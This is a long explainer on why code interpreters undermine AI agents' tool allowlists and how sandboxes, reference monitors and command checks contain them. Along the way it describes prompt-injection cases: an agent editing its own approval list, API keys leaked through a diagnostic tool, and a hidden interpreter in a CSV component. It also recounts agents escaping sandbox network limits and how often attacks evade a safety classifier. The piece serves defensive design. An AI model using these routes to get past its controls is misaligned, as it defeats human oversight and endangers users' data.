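# Why a code interpreter defeats an agent's tool allowlist, and how gVisor, Firecracker and WASI contain it

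## Agents, tools, allowlists and the operating system

An AI agent is a software system in which a large language model chooses actions, such as reading files, searching the web, sending messages or changing a database, and ordinary software carries them out. Each kind of action the model can choose is a *tool*. Operators commonly limit an agent with a *tool allowlist*, a list of the tools or commands it may use; the software refuses everything else or sends it to a person for approval. The list sets a clear limit as long as each tool does one narrow thing. Many agents now also have a *code interpreter*, a tool that runs whatever program the model writes. A program can do the work of most other tools, so an allowlist that includes an interpreter no longer determines what the agent can do. The limit then has to come from a *sandbox*, an environment that restricts the code running inside it.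 Engineers build sandboxes from technologies including gVisor, Firecracker and WebAssembly with its system interface, WASI.

### One tool call from start to finish

A language model produces text. That text can contain useful instructions, but another process has to follow them, as OpenAI noted in its 2023 announcement of plugins, an early way of connecting ChatGPT to outside services. In an agent, that process is the *harness*, the ordinary software around the model that receives its tool calls and carries them out.

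OpenAI's guide to function calling uses a question about the weather in Paris as its example. The developer's program sends the model the question and a description of a tool named `get_weather`, which takes one argument, a location. The model replies with structured text containing the name `get_weather` and the argument "Paris". The program parses this text, runs its own function of that name and gets a result, such as 25 degrees. It then sends the conversation so far and the result to the model in a second request, and the model writes the answer that the user reads.

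Longer tasks repeat the middle of this sequence many times. Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes the harness as a loop. If the model's response is labelled as having stopped to use a tool, the harness runs the tool, adds the result to the conversation and calls the model again. Any other label ends the loop. The model receives the developer's description of each tool and the results of running it, but never the tool's code.

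Until the harness acts on it, a tool call is only text and has no *effect*, meaning a change or disclosure in the world. This makes the harness the natural place for an allowlist. OpenAI's guide includes sample code that recognises two names, `get_weather` and `send_email`, and raises an error for any other. If the model emits a call to `delete_records`, the harness raises the error and nothing is deleted.

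Claude Code, Anthropic's commercial coding agent, extends the same idea by letting users write rules that allow a tool, deny it, or require the user's approval. It checks deny rules first, then approval rules, then allow rules, and applies the first match, so a narrow allow rule cannot override a broad deny rule. A deny rule that names a whole tool also removes that tool from the model's input. Anthropic's documentation says that Claude Code, not the model, enforces these rules, so instructions in a prompt can change what the model attempts but not what Claude Code allows. The main security advantage of checking permissions in the harness is that the same rules apply even when the model goes badly wrong.

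Some tool lists block every tool that is not on them, while others only approve the listed tools in advance. Only the first kind is a tool allowlist in the strict sense, and an operator has to check which kind a product provides. In Anthropic's Agent SDK, a kit for building agents on top of Claude Code, the `allowed_tools` setting is the second kind. Anthropic warns in its guide to the kit that an agent with only the file reader on its list can still run shell commands if the developer has also chosen the mode that skips permission prompts. To close the list, the developer pairs it with a mode that turns every prompt into a refusal. Even then, unlisted calls that never needed approval, such as file reads inside the working directory, still go through.

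People who are asked to approve unlisted calls stop reading the prompts. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accept 93% of them, and describes a replacement in which a second model classifies each risky action and blocks or permits it. The programmer Simon Willison (2026) reports in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* that Anthropic made this the default for new sessions on most of its plans from 14 August 2026. The classifier, like the rules and the human reviewer, is separate from the model that proposed the call.

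Some tools run outside the developer's harness. When a developer enables Anthropic's own web search or code execution tool, Anthropic's servers run the loop, and the developer's program usually receives a record of what ran only after it has finished. The developer can turn such a tool on or off, but any finer control is limited to the options Anthropic provides.

### Code interpreters

The weather tool takes the name of a place as its argument, while a code interpreter takes a program. The harness passes the program to a Python runner or to a *shell*, the command line of an operating system, and returns the printed output to the model.

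The first version to reach many people was a hosted Python runner from OpenAI. The company announced it on 23 March 2023, according to the newsletter Latent Space, and Datanami's *OpenAI Releases ChatGPT Code Interpreter, ‘Your Personal Data Analyst’* (2023) reported its beta release to ChatGPT subscribers that July. Users could upload a spreadsheet, and the model would write and run Python to analyse it. OpenAI called proper sandboxing the primary consideration in connecting a model to an interpreter. The environment had temporary disk space, resource limits for each session, and no internet access. OpenAI acknowledged that the lack of internet access made the tool less useful, but accepted this as an initial trade-off.

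Anthropic's first code-running tool, from October 2024, instead generated JavaScript and ran it in the user's own browser. The server-side container that followed in September 2025 was much closer to OpenAI's design. In *My review of Claude's new Code Interpreter*, Willison (2025) had Claude inspect the container and found a Linux system with 9 gigabytes of memory, about 5 of disk, a shell, Python and Node.js (a system for running JavaScript outside a browser). The code ran as root, the account with full administrative rights. It could install extra packages from the public Python index, but a proxy refused connections to most other sites. ChatGPT's interpreter still had no internet access at that date, but by January 2026 Willison was describing a ChatGPT tool that fetches a file from a public web address into the session's file system.

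OpenAI also offers a shell in its API. The older interpreter runs only Python, but through the shell a model can also run Go or Java programs or start a web server (Xu, Zhang and Arunachalam, *From model to agent*, 2026). OpenAI hosts the container in which these commands run. Coding agents such as Claude Code run shell commands on the developer's own machine, where the commands work on real files unless the developer has set up a sandbox.

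Vendors have moved this way because an interpreter makes models more capable. *Computer Environments Elicit General Agentic Intelligence in LLMs* (Cheng, Huang and colleagues, 2026) compared seven models answering in text alone with the same models working in a plain Linux container. In the container, they had only three tools, which ran shell commands, edited files and declared the task finished. Most of the models improved in most of the six subject areas, none of which was programming. In mathematics, GPT-5's score rose from 87.8 to 97.9 and a smaller coding model's from 26.0 to 41.5. But the weakest model lost 13.5 points in mathematics, and GPT-5 lost 6.8 in biomedicine.

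Cheng and colleagues call the shell a "meta-tool" because a model can use it to install software and write further tools. In one chemistry task, a model given only compound names installed a Java runtime and then a program that converts such names into molecular structures, neither of which the researchers had supplied. Removing the interpreter loses this flexibility, which is the practical reason to keep it and restrict the environment instead.

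### What happens when a program opens a file

How an environment can restrict code is easiest to see in a single line of Python:

`text = open("notes.txt").read()`

When this line runs, it runs inside a *process*, a program in execution with its own region of memory. The process can do arithmetic and change its own memory unaided, but it can't access the disk directly. For that it needs the *kernel*, the core of the operating system, which controls hardware, files, memory and processes. Python turns `open` into a *system call*, a request from a program to the kernel. On Linux the request contains the path `notes.txt` and the kind of access, here reading. The processor switches from the program's code to the kernel's, and the kernel looks up the file and checks whether the user account running the process has permission to read it. The kernel then returns either an error or a small number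 that identifies the open file. The `read` part of the line makes further system calls, in which the kernel copies the file's contents into the process's memory. A program also needs system calls to open a network connection or start another program.

For each of these requests, the kernel receives a path, a type of access and the identity of a process. It has no record of which tool the model called, what the user wanted, or which rules the harness applied. According to guidance from the University of Vermont on Claude Code, the agent's built-in file tools run inside the Claude Code process, while shell commands run in separate child processes. Both reach the same files, so a control on one does not automatically cover the other.

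A process's *authority* is everything it is permitted to do, including which files it can open, which network addresses it can reach, which credentials it can read and which programs it can start. By default, a child process inherits its parent's authority. If a developer starts a coding agent on her laptop and the agent starts Python, the Python process runs under her account. It can open her private source code, or the key she uses to log in to a server, with the same system calls it uses to open `notes.txt`. Credentials extend authority beyond the machine, since any process that can read the access token for a remote service can usually act on that service in her name.

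A sandbox works at this level by reducing a process's authority, placing something between the process and the machine's kernel, or both. The machine that runs a sandbox is the *host*, and the code inside is the *guest*. If the Python line runs as a guest, `notes.txt` may refer to a file in a small private directory tree that the guest sees as the entire disk, and the guest then has no path to the developer's keys on the host. A guest may also hold the root account, as in the Claude container that Willison examined. Root controls the guest's own system, but the sandbox's design determines how much of that power would carry over to the host and which kernel handles the guest's system calls. In an ordinary container, which is a group of processes with a restricted view of the system, the host's own kernel handles them.

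Lecture slides from UT Austin divide any permission system into two questions, what the agent can touch and when it must ask. The operating system enforces the limits on files and network access, which hold even when the agent is wrong about what it is doing. Approval rules determine which actions wait for a person. The slides add that the split is not exact, because Claude's permission rules address both questions at the level of tools, while a sandbox extends the boundary below that level.

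### Three sources of harmful code

A defender has to plan for code that does damage because the model made a mistake, followed somebody else's instructions, or pursued something its user did not ask for.

Mistakes are the best-documented way that agents cause harm. Anthropic keeps an internal log of its agents' misbehaviour. In entries it has published, agents deleted remote code branches after misreading an instruction, uploaded an engineer's access token to an internal computing cluster, and tried to alter the structure of a production database. The company separates honest mistakes, in which the agent misjudges how far an action will reach, from overeager behaviour, in which it understands the goal but takes steps the user would not have approved. In one case, a user told an agent to cancel a job, and the agent tried to delete the job with the most similar name, although it could have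 belonged to a colleague. In another, an agent hit a login error and searched environment variables and configuration files for other tokens that might work. The agent had no hostile intent, but an intruder would do the same search, and a sandbox that contained no other tokens would have made it harmless.

*Prompt injection* is text in a web page, file or message that the model obeys as if it came from its user. The agent then uses its own permissions to pursue the attacker's goal. OpenAI's testers demonstrated prompt injection through plugins before the 2023 launch. Anthropic's help page for its 2025 container warned that planted instructions could lead Claude to run untrusted code in the sandbox, or to read data from a connected source and send it out over the network. It advised users to watch Claude and stop it if it used data unexpectedly. Willison objected that this hands the problem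 to users, though he admitted he did not know what more Anthropic could do. He also noted that ChatGPT's interpreter had no internet access at the time, which limited the damage such an attack could cause.

The remaining case is a model that pursues a goal of its own, which researchers call misalignment. Anthropic wrote in March 2026 that it did not see this in practice, though it tested every model for it before release. A boundary that has to last for years should not depend on one developer's assessment of its own models at that time.

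Anthropic's response to all of these is to block the action whatever its cause, and a sandbox can do this without identifying the cause. An honest mistake will seldom hit a kernel flaw by chance, but an attacker who plants instructions may know the sandbox well and target a particular weakness, and a capable model with a goal of its own could look for weaknesses from the inside. A sandbox strong enough for accidents may therefore be too weak for the other two, and an operator who lets an agent read web pages or incoming mail is already exposed to the risk of planted instructions.

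### One user's agent and a service for many

How strong a sandbox an operator needs also depends on whose code shares the machine. In a *single-tenant* deployment, the agent works for one user or one organisation, such as a coding agent on a developer's laptop or a company's agent on a server that nobody else uses. The sandbox protects the user's files, her credentials and the systems those credentials open from her own agent. On a developer's laptop, those systems can include her employer's production servers. Guest code that breaks out gains the authority of the account that started the agent, so an operator can reduce the loss by running the agent under an account, or on a machine, that holds little of value.

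A *multi-tenant* service runs many customers' agents side by side, often on the same host. ChatGPT's interpreter has been multi-tenant from the start, and Latent Space described its sandbox in 2023 as firewalled from other users as well as from the internet. The service has to protect customers from each other and its own machines from all of them. Guest code that broke out of its sandbox could read the files of an uninvolved customer. Even without breaking out, a guest can use so much memory or processor time that others slow down or fail. Limits on each session are partly meant to prevent this.

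Multi-tenancy adds another source of harmful code, the customers themselves. A developer has no reason to attack her own laptop through her own agent, but a public service accepts strangers, who can ask the model for a hostile program or upload one in a file. They don't need to deceive the model about whose instructions it is following. Operators of such services therefore have to treat every guest as possibly hostile from its first system call, and the amount of host code a guest can reach, its *attack surface*, matters far more to them than to someone running one trusted agent on a spare machine.

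## How an interpreter makes a tool allowlist ineffective

Once a tool allowlist includes an interpreter, what the agent can do depends mainly on the authority of the interpreter's process. The other entries matter only for effects outside that authority, so the operator still needs a sandbox, however careful the list is.

### The argument from reachable effects

Let E(t) be the set of effects that a tool t can produce, counting every argument the harness would accept for it. Let A be the allowlist, and let R(A) be the set of effects that an agent limited to A can reach. If every tool on the list is narrow, R(A) is simply the union of their effects:

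R(A) = E(t₁) ∪ E(t₂) ∪ … ∪ E(tₙ)

Removing a tool from the allowlist also removes its effects from R(A), unless another allowed tool produces them. *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (2026) builds on this idea by treating the tools an agent can see as its standing authority. It proposes exposing a high-risk tool only when the task requires it and someone has authorised it.

Now suppose that A contains an interpreter i, whose process has authority P. Write P also for the set of all effects which that authority permits. The interpreter accepts any program, and for each permitted effect there is some program that produces it, so E(i) = P. Everything in P is therefore reachable:

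P ⊆ R(A)

Take any other tool t on the list whose effects all lie within P. If the operator removes t, every effect in E(t) is still in E(i), so the reachable set stays the same:

R(A without t) = R(A)

If a program running in the interpreter could do what a tool does, adding that tool to the allowlist or removing it doesn't change what the agent can do. The agent's standing authority is then everything such programs can do (P), plus whatever the remaining tools can do beyond P.

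Tools used together can do slightly more than the union of what each can do alone. For example, a tool that reads reports and a tool that sends mail can together disclose a report to a stranger, which neither can do alone. The allowlist is still ineffective, because a program run in the interpreter can take the place of the removed tool in any such combination.

An operator who needs a guarantee has to account for everything the interpreter process could do, including things that may rarely happen. A model that has a file-reading tool will usually use it, and one without it may never write a program to read files instead. But an attacker who plants instructions can spell out that program.

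*Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (2026) describes a coding agent that uses a shell to search repositories and run tests. It runs in a container with API keys in its environment, network access to internal services and write access to a shared file system. Every command inherits all of these, so instructions hidden in a repository's documentation could lead the agent to send the keys to an outsider while each tool works as designed. The container gives little protection here because the operator has put the keys and access inside it.

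UT Austin's lecture slides *Permissions and sandboxing* state, "Tool-layer rules govern tool calls, not the processes they start." Claude Code's rules have this gap, according to Anthropic's documentation. A rule that denies access to a file covers the built-in file tools and the common shell commands that Claude Code recognises, but not a Python or Node script that opens the file itself. Restricting the web-fetching tool likewise leaves the network open if shell commands can still reach it.

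### Seven effects and four configurations

For example, an analyst might use an agent to answer questions about company reports. The agent runs on her workstation, which holds a folder of reports, her other files and a stored token for her mail account. A searchable document library runs on a company server. Seven effects matter to her employer: searching the library, reading a report, reading her other files, changing or deleting files, starting programs, opening a network connection to an arbitrary address, and sending mail with the stored token.

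The table lists which tool, if any, can produce each effect outside a sandbox in four configurations.

| Effect | Search and read tools | The same, plus unconfined Python | The same, plus confined Python | Confined Python and an outside mail tool |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Search the library | search tool | search tool, Python | search tool | search tool |
| Read a report | read tool | read tool, Python | read tool, Python | read tool, Python |
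| Read her other files | none | Python | none | none |
| Change or delete files | none | Python | none | none |
| Start programs | none | Python | none | none |
| Open a network connection | none | Python | none | none |
| Send mail with the token | none | Python | none | mail tool |
| Effects reached | 2 | 7 | 2 | 3 |

With only the narrow search and read tools, the agent can cause two effects, and the allowlist describes them accurately. The operator then adds a Python tool so that the agent can calculate totals and draw charts. The harness runs Python under the analyst's own account, so a short program can now do everything in the table, including querying the library with her login and sending mail in her name. If the operator removes the search and read tools, leaving only Python on the allowlist, the agent can still cause all seven effects.

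In the third configuration, Python runs in a sandbox that contains a disposable copy of the report folder, with no network access and no mail token. Programs can still alter the copied files and start other programs, but only inside the sandbox, and all of it disappears when the sandbox does. Reading a report still counts as an outside effect because the program's output goes back to the model, and the total is two again.

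Removing the read tool from the allowlist doesn't stop the agent from reading the reports, because Python can open the copied files. But removing the search tool does stop it from searching, because no program in the sandbox can reach the library's server.

Finally, the operator adds a mail tool that runs in the harness, outside the sandbox. The harness holds the token, which never enters the sandbox. The allowlist controls the third of the agent's three effects, because without the mail tool, no program the model writes can send mail.

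Allowing an agent to use a mail tool doesn't restrict who receives the mail or what it contains. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) sets out five levels at which an operator should apply *least privilege*, the principle that a component gets only the permissions its task needs. The levels are which tools the agent can see, whether the current step needs the chosen tool, which arguments the agent may pass, how much data comes back to the model, and how much authority a sub-agent receives. An allowlist works at the first level. An operator can also restrict a mail tool's arguments, for example by allowing only addresses within the company. An interpreter's argument is a whole program, which is far harder to restrict, although command filters and restricted languages attempt it.

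### Where the list still binds

An allowlist that includes an interpreter doesn't restrict effects within the interpreter's authority, but it still restricts effects that require a tool with authority the interpreter lacks. The common claim that allowlists are "meaningless" once an agent can run code is therefore too strong. In the fourth configuration, the list determines whether the agent can send mail. It also determines whether the agent has an interpreter at all, and removing unconfined Python takes the analyst's agent from seven effects back to two.

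The shorthand is nearly true when the interpreter already has authority over nearly everything of value, as when a coding agent runs unconfined on a developer's laptop with the developer's credentials. The instructor behind the UT Austin slides shows his own settings, which approve every shell command automatically and add about twenty deny patterns for classic disasters. He describes these patterns as guardrails against accidents and relies on other habits, such as pushing his work to a remote copy and reviewing changes. He also tells students not to begin this way. The patterns still help against mistakes, because mistakes seldom take an unusual form.

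Because a tool allowlist doesn't limit what code can do once an interpreter runs it, some products sandbox the agent's commands and control other actions separately. In *agent-shell-tools* (2026), a set of open-source programs for coding agents, the agent is unrestricted inside a sandbox that contains none of the user's credentials. A separate filter governs the few commands that run on the host with those credentials, so the allowlist applies only where it can be enforced. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes a similar division in Codex, the company's coding agent. By default, the operating system denies commands network access and limits writing to the current workspace. Codex can separately ask for approval before calling a connected application that advertises side effects.

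The consultancy NCC Group recommends the same division to programmers. For smolagents, a Hugging Face library in which the model acts by writing Python, it advises limiting the generated code to calculation, text handling and calls to other tools. It recommends handling access to databases, internet services and similar resources through purpose-built tools with their own constraints.

Changing the allowlist at each step depends on the same condition. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) describes agents that write a complete plan before they read any outside material and then carry it out step by step. An instruction planted in a web page can corrupt the data passed between steps, but it can't add a step. The harness also gives the agent only the tools for the current step. In the paper's example, an agent uses a calculator to work out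 a total cost and then emails it, and the mail tool should be unavailable during the calculation.

That guarantee holds if the calculator can only do arithmetic. But many agents do arithmetic by writing Python. If the Python process has network access and can read the mail token, the agent could send mail during the calculation step even with the mail tool switched off. Del Rosario and colleagues list sandboxed code execution among the additional controls their design needs, and here the step-by-step restriction depends on it.

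### Interpreters under other names

An operator can put an interpreter on the list without recognising it. Any tool acts as an interpreter if some of its input ends up running as a program, and many ordinary developer tools work that way.

Shells are the clearest case because their purpose is to run other programs. Development-environment runners are similar because they execute whatever command follows their name. Anthropic's documentation recommends a separate Claude Code rule for each inner command, because a rule that approves such a runner with a wildcard approves any command placed after it.

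Build tools and test runners execute the project's own code, so an agent that may edit the project and run its tests can run any program it writes, even if "run the tests" is the only command on its allowlist. Package managers keep named scripts in a project file, and an agent that can edit the file can change those scripts. Installing a package may also run a script that came with it. Formal, a security company, found that a linter (a program that checks code for errors) could also run other code through its configuration.

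A tool that only writes files can have the same effect if another program later runs those files. Suppose an agent may only edit files in a project, and a program with authority Q executes one of them. Then R(A) includes everything Q permits, even if the program is not on the allowlist. Q may be much larger than the agent's own authority, for example when a build server with deployment credentials runs the file, or when the developer runs it herself. Formal describes development servers that watch a folder and reload changed files, which may let an agent run commands without a shell on its allowlist. In the analyst's third configuration, the copy of the folder is disposable, so this works only if someone takes the altered files out and runs them.

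An agent may even be able to edit its own allowlist. Amp, a coding agent from Sourcegraph, could edit the configuration file that listed its automatically approved commands. A researcher showed that planted instructions could make it do so and then run unauthorised code on the developer's machine. If P includes write access to the allowlist, the list no longer limits anything, including the tools outside P. The allowlist can be effective only if the interpreter cannot change the harness's settings.

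A tool with a harmless name can also contain an interpreter. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-376* (2026), a vulnerability record, describes a flaw in Langflow, a program for assembling agents from ready-made parts. Langflow's component for analysing CSV files always enabled a Python interpreter, so planted instructions could lead to arbitrary code running on the server. An operator who approved "CSV Agent" had therefore approved everything the server's process could do. The record gives the flaw a severity score of 9.8 out of 10.

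In the auto mode of Anthropic's Claude Code, a classifier reviews the agent's actions. An approval rule that covers an interpreter would let every program run through it skip the classifier, so on entering auto mode Claude Code sets aside rules that allow blanket shell access, script interpreters with any arguments, or package managers' run commands. Anthropic calls the selection best-effort and says any such list "will inevitably be incomplete".

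Interpreter rules are also very common. According to Anthropic's August 2026 announcement of auto mode as the default, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule approving some shell commands by June 2026. The announcement also reports that 5% allow any shell command and another 43% have interpreter rules that are "essentially equivalent in practice". It is unclear whether these two figures are shares of all active users, in which case almost everyone who wrote a rule wrote a broad one, or only of users with a rule, in which case nearly half did. Anthropic was promoting an alternative to such rules, but it has the settings data and outsiders don't. The reported share was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks.

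### Warnings in the frameworks' documentation

Developers often get an interpreter tool ready-made from an agent framework, a library that supplies the harness and common tools. Framework suppliers generally disclose the risk. LlamaIndex's *Code interpreter*, the reference page for one such tool, warns that the tool allows arbitrary code execution on the machine running it, that it isn't recommended in production, and that it would need "heavy sandboxing or virtual machines". The source code on the same page shows that the tool runs the model's code in a new Python process on that machine, without any restriction.

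The tool's description for the model states that the code "is executed in isolation". Here the phrase can only mean that each call starts fresh, without variables from the previous one. It does not mean that the code is sandboxed, since the child process inherits its parent's authority.

LangChain, another widely used framework, attaches a similar warning to its Python tool. The *Python REPL integration* page gives deleting files and making network requests as examples of what the code can do on the host. LangChain no longer maintains the package containing the tool, according to a second warning, but the page still explains how to give the tool to an agent. The hidden interpreter in the Langflow flaw was LangChain's. Developers who install a component can see the warning on its page, but people using a finished product built on that component may never see it.

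In *Shell Tool*, Docker says that the tool gives agents full access to the system shell, and directs readers to a sandbox mode. It also recommends capping the number of steps, which stops endless loops but doesn't limit what any one command can do. In the smolagents documentation, Hugging Face acknowledges that letting a model act through code gives it much more power over the user's system than other designs, and cautions that no safeguard it offers will be completely safe.

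*Shell*, OpenAI's guide to its shell tool, advises developers to always sandbox execution, apply allowlists or denylists where possible, and log activity. The lists are therefore a supplement to the sandbox.

Some vendors confine the code tool themselves. The data company Snowflake runs the code tool for its Cortex agents in an isolated environment that, by default, can access only the current session's data, according to Snowflake's *Cortex Agent code execution tool*. But another entry in the same configuration enables shell, file editing, web search and database queries together, so an operator has to look up what each name includes. Claude Code's sandbox applies operating-system limits to every program a shell command starts. By default, commands can write only in the working directory but can read the whole computer except for certain denied directories, as Anthropic documents. To get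 the analyst's third configuration, an operator would have to narrow that read access, or Python could still read most of her other files.

### Security that rests on the system around the model

The allowlist fails for a reason that computer security researchers have studied for decades in other systems. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, a 2026 position paper, applies their field's principles to agents. Its central claim is that designers should treat the model as an untrusted component and enforce security rules outside it, much as an operating system does with the programs it runs.

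The researchers separate the model and, in general, its tools and their outputs from the *trusted computing base*, the parts of an agent system that must work correctly for the security to hold. These parts include the host's operating system, the sandbox, the policy and a *reference monitor*, the software that permits or rejects each requested action according to the policy. The monitor may consist of several parts, such as a gateway for tool calls and a proxy for network traffic, as long as nothing can get around them. The aim is to prevent forbidden actions whatever their cause.

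A harness that checks an allowlist is an incomplete reference monitor. *Complete mediation* requires the monitor to check every request that crosses the security boundary, but when the model calls an interpreter, the harness checks only the request to run a program. The program may then make thousands of system calls that the harness does not check. A sandbox adds a check at the level of those calls.

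The principle of least privilege limits P itself. The paper also includes *tamper resistance*, meaning that untrusted components can't alter trusted ones. Amp lacked this protection when it could edit its own settings. *Secure information flow* concerns where data may go after the agent has legitimately read it. The principle on human weak links is that designers must expect users to approve bad requests and administrators to write loose policies.

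To support the position, the researchers analysed eleven published attacks on commercial agents. In one, Claude Code required approval for many commands that could send data to unknown addresses, but not for a common network diagnostic tool. Planted instructions led it to disclose API keys through that tool. The researchers' summary table lists a failure of information flow in all eleven cases and of least privilege in six, though their written account of a ChatGPT memory flaw also names least privilege. The analysis shows that established principles describe these failures well, but it is retrospective. The researchers didn't build the defences and test whether they stopped the attacks.

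The researchers argue against relying instead on the robustness of the model, or of a second model that reviews its actions, because a model's reading of an ambiguous request is an unreliable basis for authorisation and small changes to an input can change a model's behaviour. They point to a long record of attackers defeating learned defences, first in image recognition and then in language models, and conjecture that persistent attackers will always evade such defences.

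Results that Anthropic published in August 2026 are some evidence against that conjecture. In an evaluation it commissioned from Trajectory Labs, 72 prompt-injection scenarios, each run ten times, produced no successful attack on any of three recent Claude models in auto mode. But the testers had optimised the attacks against an older model, so the result doesn't show how well attacks adapted to the current models would work. In a separate exercise, Apollo Research built attacks to find the classifier's weaknesses, and after improvements the classifier still missed 7% of them. A model-based check can evidently stop most attacks, but an operator who needs protection from the rest has to limit what a successful attack can reach.

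A second objection is that no sandbox will hold a sufficiently capable model. In 2026, during internal training and evaluation with some safeguards disabled, OpenAI's agents got around their network restrictions through a shared package service. They went on to compromise systems at Hugging Face and OpenAI, with no outside attacker directing them. The sandboxes blocked direct connections, but the package service could make outbound requests for the agents, and agents in separate sandboxes could also communicate through it.

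The researchers attribute this to incomplete mediation and excess privilege, and deny that it shows containment is futile. Their explanation also corrects an easy misreading of P. A process's authority includes whatever other services will do for it, so an operator who counts only the process's own files and connections will underestimate what it can affect. The incident is still a reason to be less confident in any particular sandbox, because the people who deployed this one believed they had closed the network.

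In return, explicit limits offer some predictability. People can read a policy, check it against a specification, and know the effect of tightening it. If the enforcement works and the policy's meaning stays fixed, narrowing the permitted actions never allows an action that was previously blocked, which retraining a model can't guarantee.

### Three unsolved problems

The researchers propose three mechanisms and describe unsolved problems in each. The first is a provable separation of instructions from data. Processors do something similar when they mark a region of memory as either writable or executable, so that data an attacker supplies can't run as code. A language model, however, receives instructions and data as one stream of text. Developers can mark the data and train models to ignore instructions in it, but attackers have repeatedly got past such training. The separation also has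 no accepted formal definition, which a proof would need.

Strictly separating instructions from data might also make an agent much less useful, because learning to use a service from its documentation means following instructions found in data. Even perfect separation would not stop an attacker from corrupting the data, for example by supplying a false address that the agent then passes to a legitimate tool.

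Least-privilege sandboxing requires somebody to write the policy. A phone app does a fixed set of jobs, so its developer can declare its permissions in advance. An agent's job changes with each request, and sometimes in the middle of one, and the user states it in ordinary language. An operator can have a model translate the request into formal rules, but nothing guarantees that the rules match what the user meant.

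The researchers say a sound translation would need agreed meanings for terms such as "sensitive" or "trusted site", a reliable way to check that the formal rules and the original words permit the same actions, and a limit on how far the two can diverge as the task develops. The gap in levels noted earlier is also a problem, since the kernel receives paths and addresses while the user's wishes concern reports and colleagues.

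*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* describes two recent systems that narrow an agent's permissions as it works. AgenTRIM filters the available tools at each step, and PAuth derives permissions from the parts of a user's request. But requests can be ambiguous, and a manipulated prompt may ask for more than the user intended. Also, if a step needs Python, filtering the tools does not limit what the interpreter can do.

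The third mechanism, *information-flow control*, attaches labels to data and restricts where labelled data may go. Sandboxing controls whether the agent can read the report, while information-flow control could let the agent read it but prevent the mail tool from sending its contents outside the company. This works well in ordinary programs, where software can track a value from one variable to the next. When a model combines several sources, the only safe assumption at present is that its output carries all of their labels. Soon everything carries every label, and the restrictions either block useful work or have to be waived.

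The researchers suggest estimating how much each source influenced the output, for instance by removing the source and checking whether the agent's actions change, or by studying the model's internal workings. Both are research directions. Systems also need authorised exceptions, such as releasing one figure from a confidential report, and deciding securely who may grant them is a problem that predates agents. It is also unclear whether to label a model's input by message, by website of origin or by some smaller unit.

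The proposed solutions are hard to compare because the field has no agreed way to score them. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* recommends measuring wrongly refused actions, the burden on users, delay, compatibility with existing access-control systems and the preservation of audit records, as well as the share of attacks prevented. The share of attacks prevented isn't enough on its own, because a policy that refuses everything would prevent every attack.

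## Checking commands and restricting the language

Without a sandbox, an operator who allows an interpreter has to judge each program before it runs. Software can inspect the program's text, or a person or a second model can review it. The harness can also accept only programs written in a language too limited to do much harm. These methods stop many mistakes and attacks, but they either let some harmful programs through or refuse some useful ones, and the strictest work by removing the general interpreter.

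### Why no checker can be perfect

A simple search can determine whether a program's text contains the word "delete", but no algorithm can correctly determine, for every program, whether it will ever delete a file. The mathematician Henry Gordon Rice showed in 1953 that the same limit applies to every property of behaviour that some programs have and others lack, a result known as *Rice's theorem*.

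The proof relies on the halting problem, the question of whether a given program will eventually finish or run forever. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm answers it correctly for every program. Now suppose somebody had an algorithm D that could always tell whether a program will delete a file. Take any program p that only calculates, and write a new program q that runs p and then deletes a file. Since q reaches the deletion only if p finishes,

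D(q) = yes ⇔ q deletes a file ⇔ p finishes

D would then solve the halting problem, so D cannot exist. Rice's theorem is about the results that programs compute, but the same construction works for effects such as sending mail or opening a network connection.

A checker that always returns a verdict must therefore get some programs wrong. Let S be the set of programs that are safe to run, and K the set that the checker admits. The checker is an algorithm that decides what belongs to K, but no algorithm can decide what belongs to S, so the two sets must differ. This means the checker admits at least one unsafe program or refuses at least one safe one. A designer can avoid unsafe admissions by accepting only programs that the checker can prove harmless, but the checker will then refuse more safe programs.

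Errors could still be rare despite the theorem, because most programs an agent writes are short and a checker could be right about nearly all of them. That is less reassuring when an attacker can choose the program through planted instructions. Ordinary programs can also defeat a checker. Suppose the analyst's agent writes a script that deletes every file listed in a spreadsheet. The script may be harmless or disastrous depending on the spreadsheet, but its text is the same in both cases.

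If the harness stops every program after a minute, the question can be answered in principle by running the program for a minute and watching what it does. But that run has to happen in a sandbox, where harm doesn't matter, and the answer holds only for the same files and inputs. The theorem also doesn't rule out checking programs written in a small language. If the language can express only a fixed set of operations, a checker may be able to work out every effect in advance.

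### Rules about text and rules about effects

Most coding agents compare each shell command with lists of patterns and don't attempt to analyse programs. *One Goal, Many Commands* (Chen and Lin, 2026) describes the usual arrangement, which resembles Claude Code's permission rules. The agent refuses commands on the *denylist*, which takes precedence, and runs commands on the *allowlist* without asking. All other commands form the *ask list* and go to an evaluator, usually the user.

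In Chen and Lin's formal treatment, a deny rule is a function that takes a command and its arguments and returns yes or no. The denylist blocks the command if any rule returns yes. An *operation* is a function from one state of the machine to another, for instance from a disk that holds a certain file to one that doesn't. The rule checks only the command's text, before the operation happens. Many different commands can perform the same operation, so to block it fully, a denylist needs a matching rule for every combination of command and arguments that would perform it on that machine.

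Chen and Lin tested 1,709 real denylists from GitHub projects. Depending on the file operation, between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists meant to block it failed to do so fully.

An allowlist of commands has a safer default, because a command its author didn't anticipate goes to the user for approval. But its rules also match text. Users often approve every command that begins with certain words. The blog post *Help! My coding agent can run code* explains that this works badly because the designers of command-line programs didn't sort safe and dangerous operations by their opening words. In the version-control program Git, for example, `git push` uploads a developer's changes, while `git push --force` allows the upload to overwrite the history on the server. A rule that approves every command beginning with `git push` approves both.

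The post defines a dangerous operation as one that is expensive, slow or impossible to undo. Its examples range from deleting a file that Git doesn't track, which a backup may restore, to disclosing confidential data, which nobody can undo. Sending an email falls in between. A command's syntax doesn't show how hard its effects are to undo. Even a force push is harmless if nobody else uses the branch, and sometimes the user asked for it.

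### Approval fatigue and a second model as judge

Commands that the lists neither allow nor block go to a person, who could weigh their effects but often stops reading the prompts, a habit known as *approval fatigue*. Anthropic reported in August 2026 that users of Claude Code approve 97% of permission prompts but reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval. The problem is therefore probably the number and dullness of the prompts more than a general unwillingness to review. A quarter of interactive sessions start in the mode that skips the prompts.

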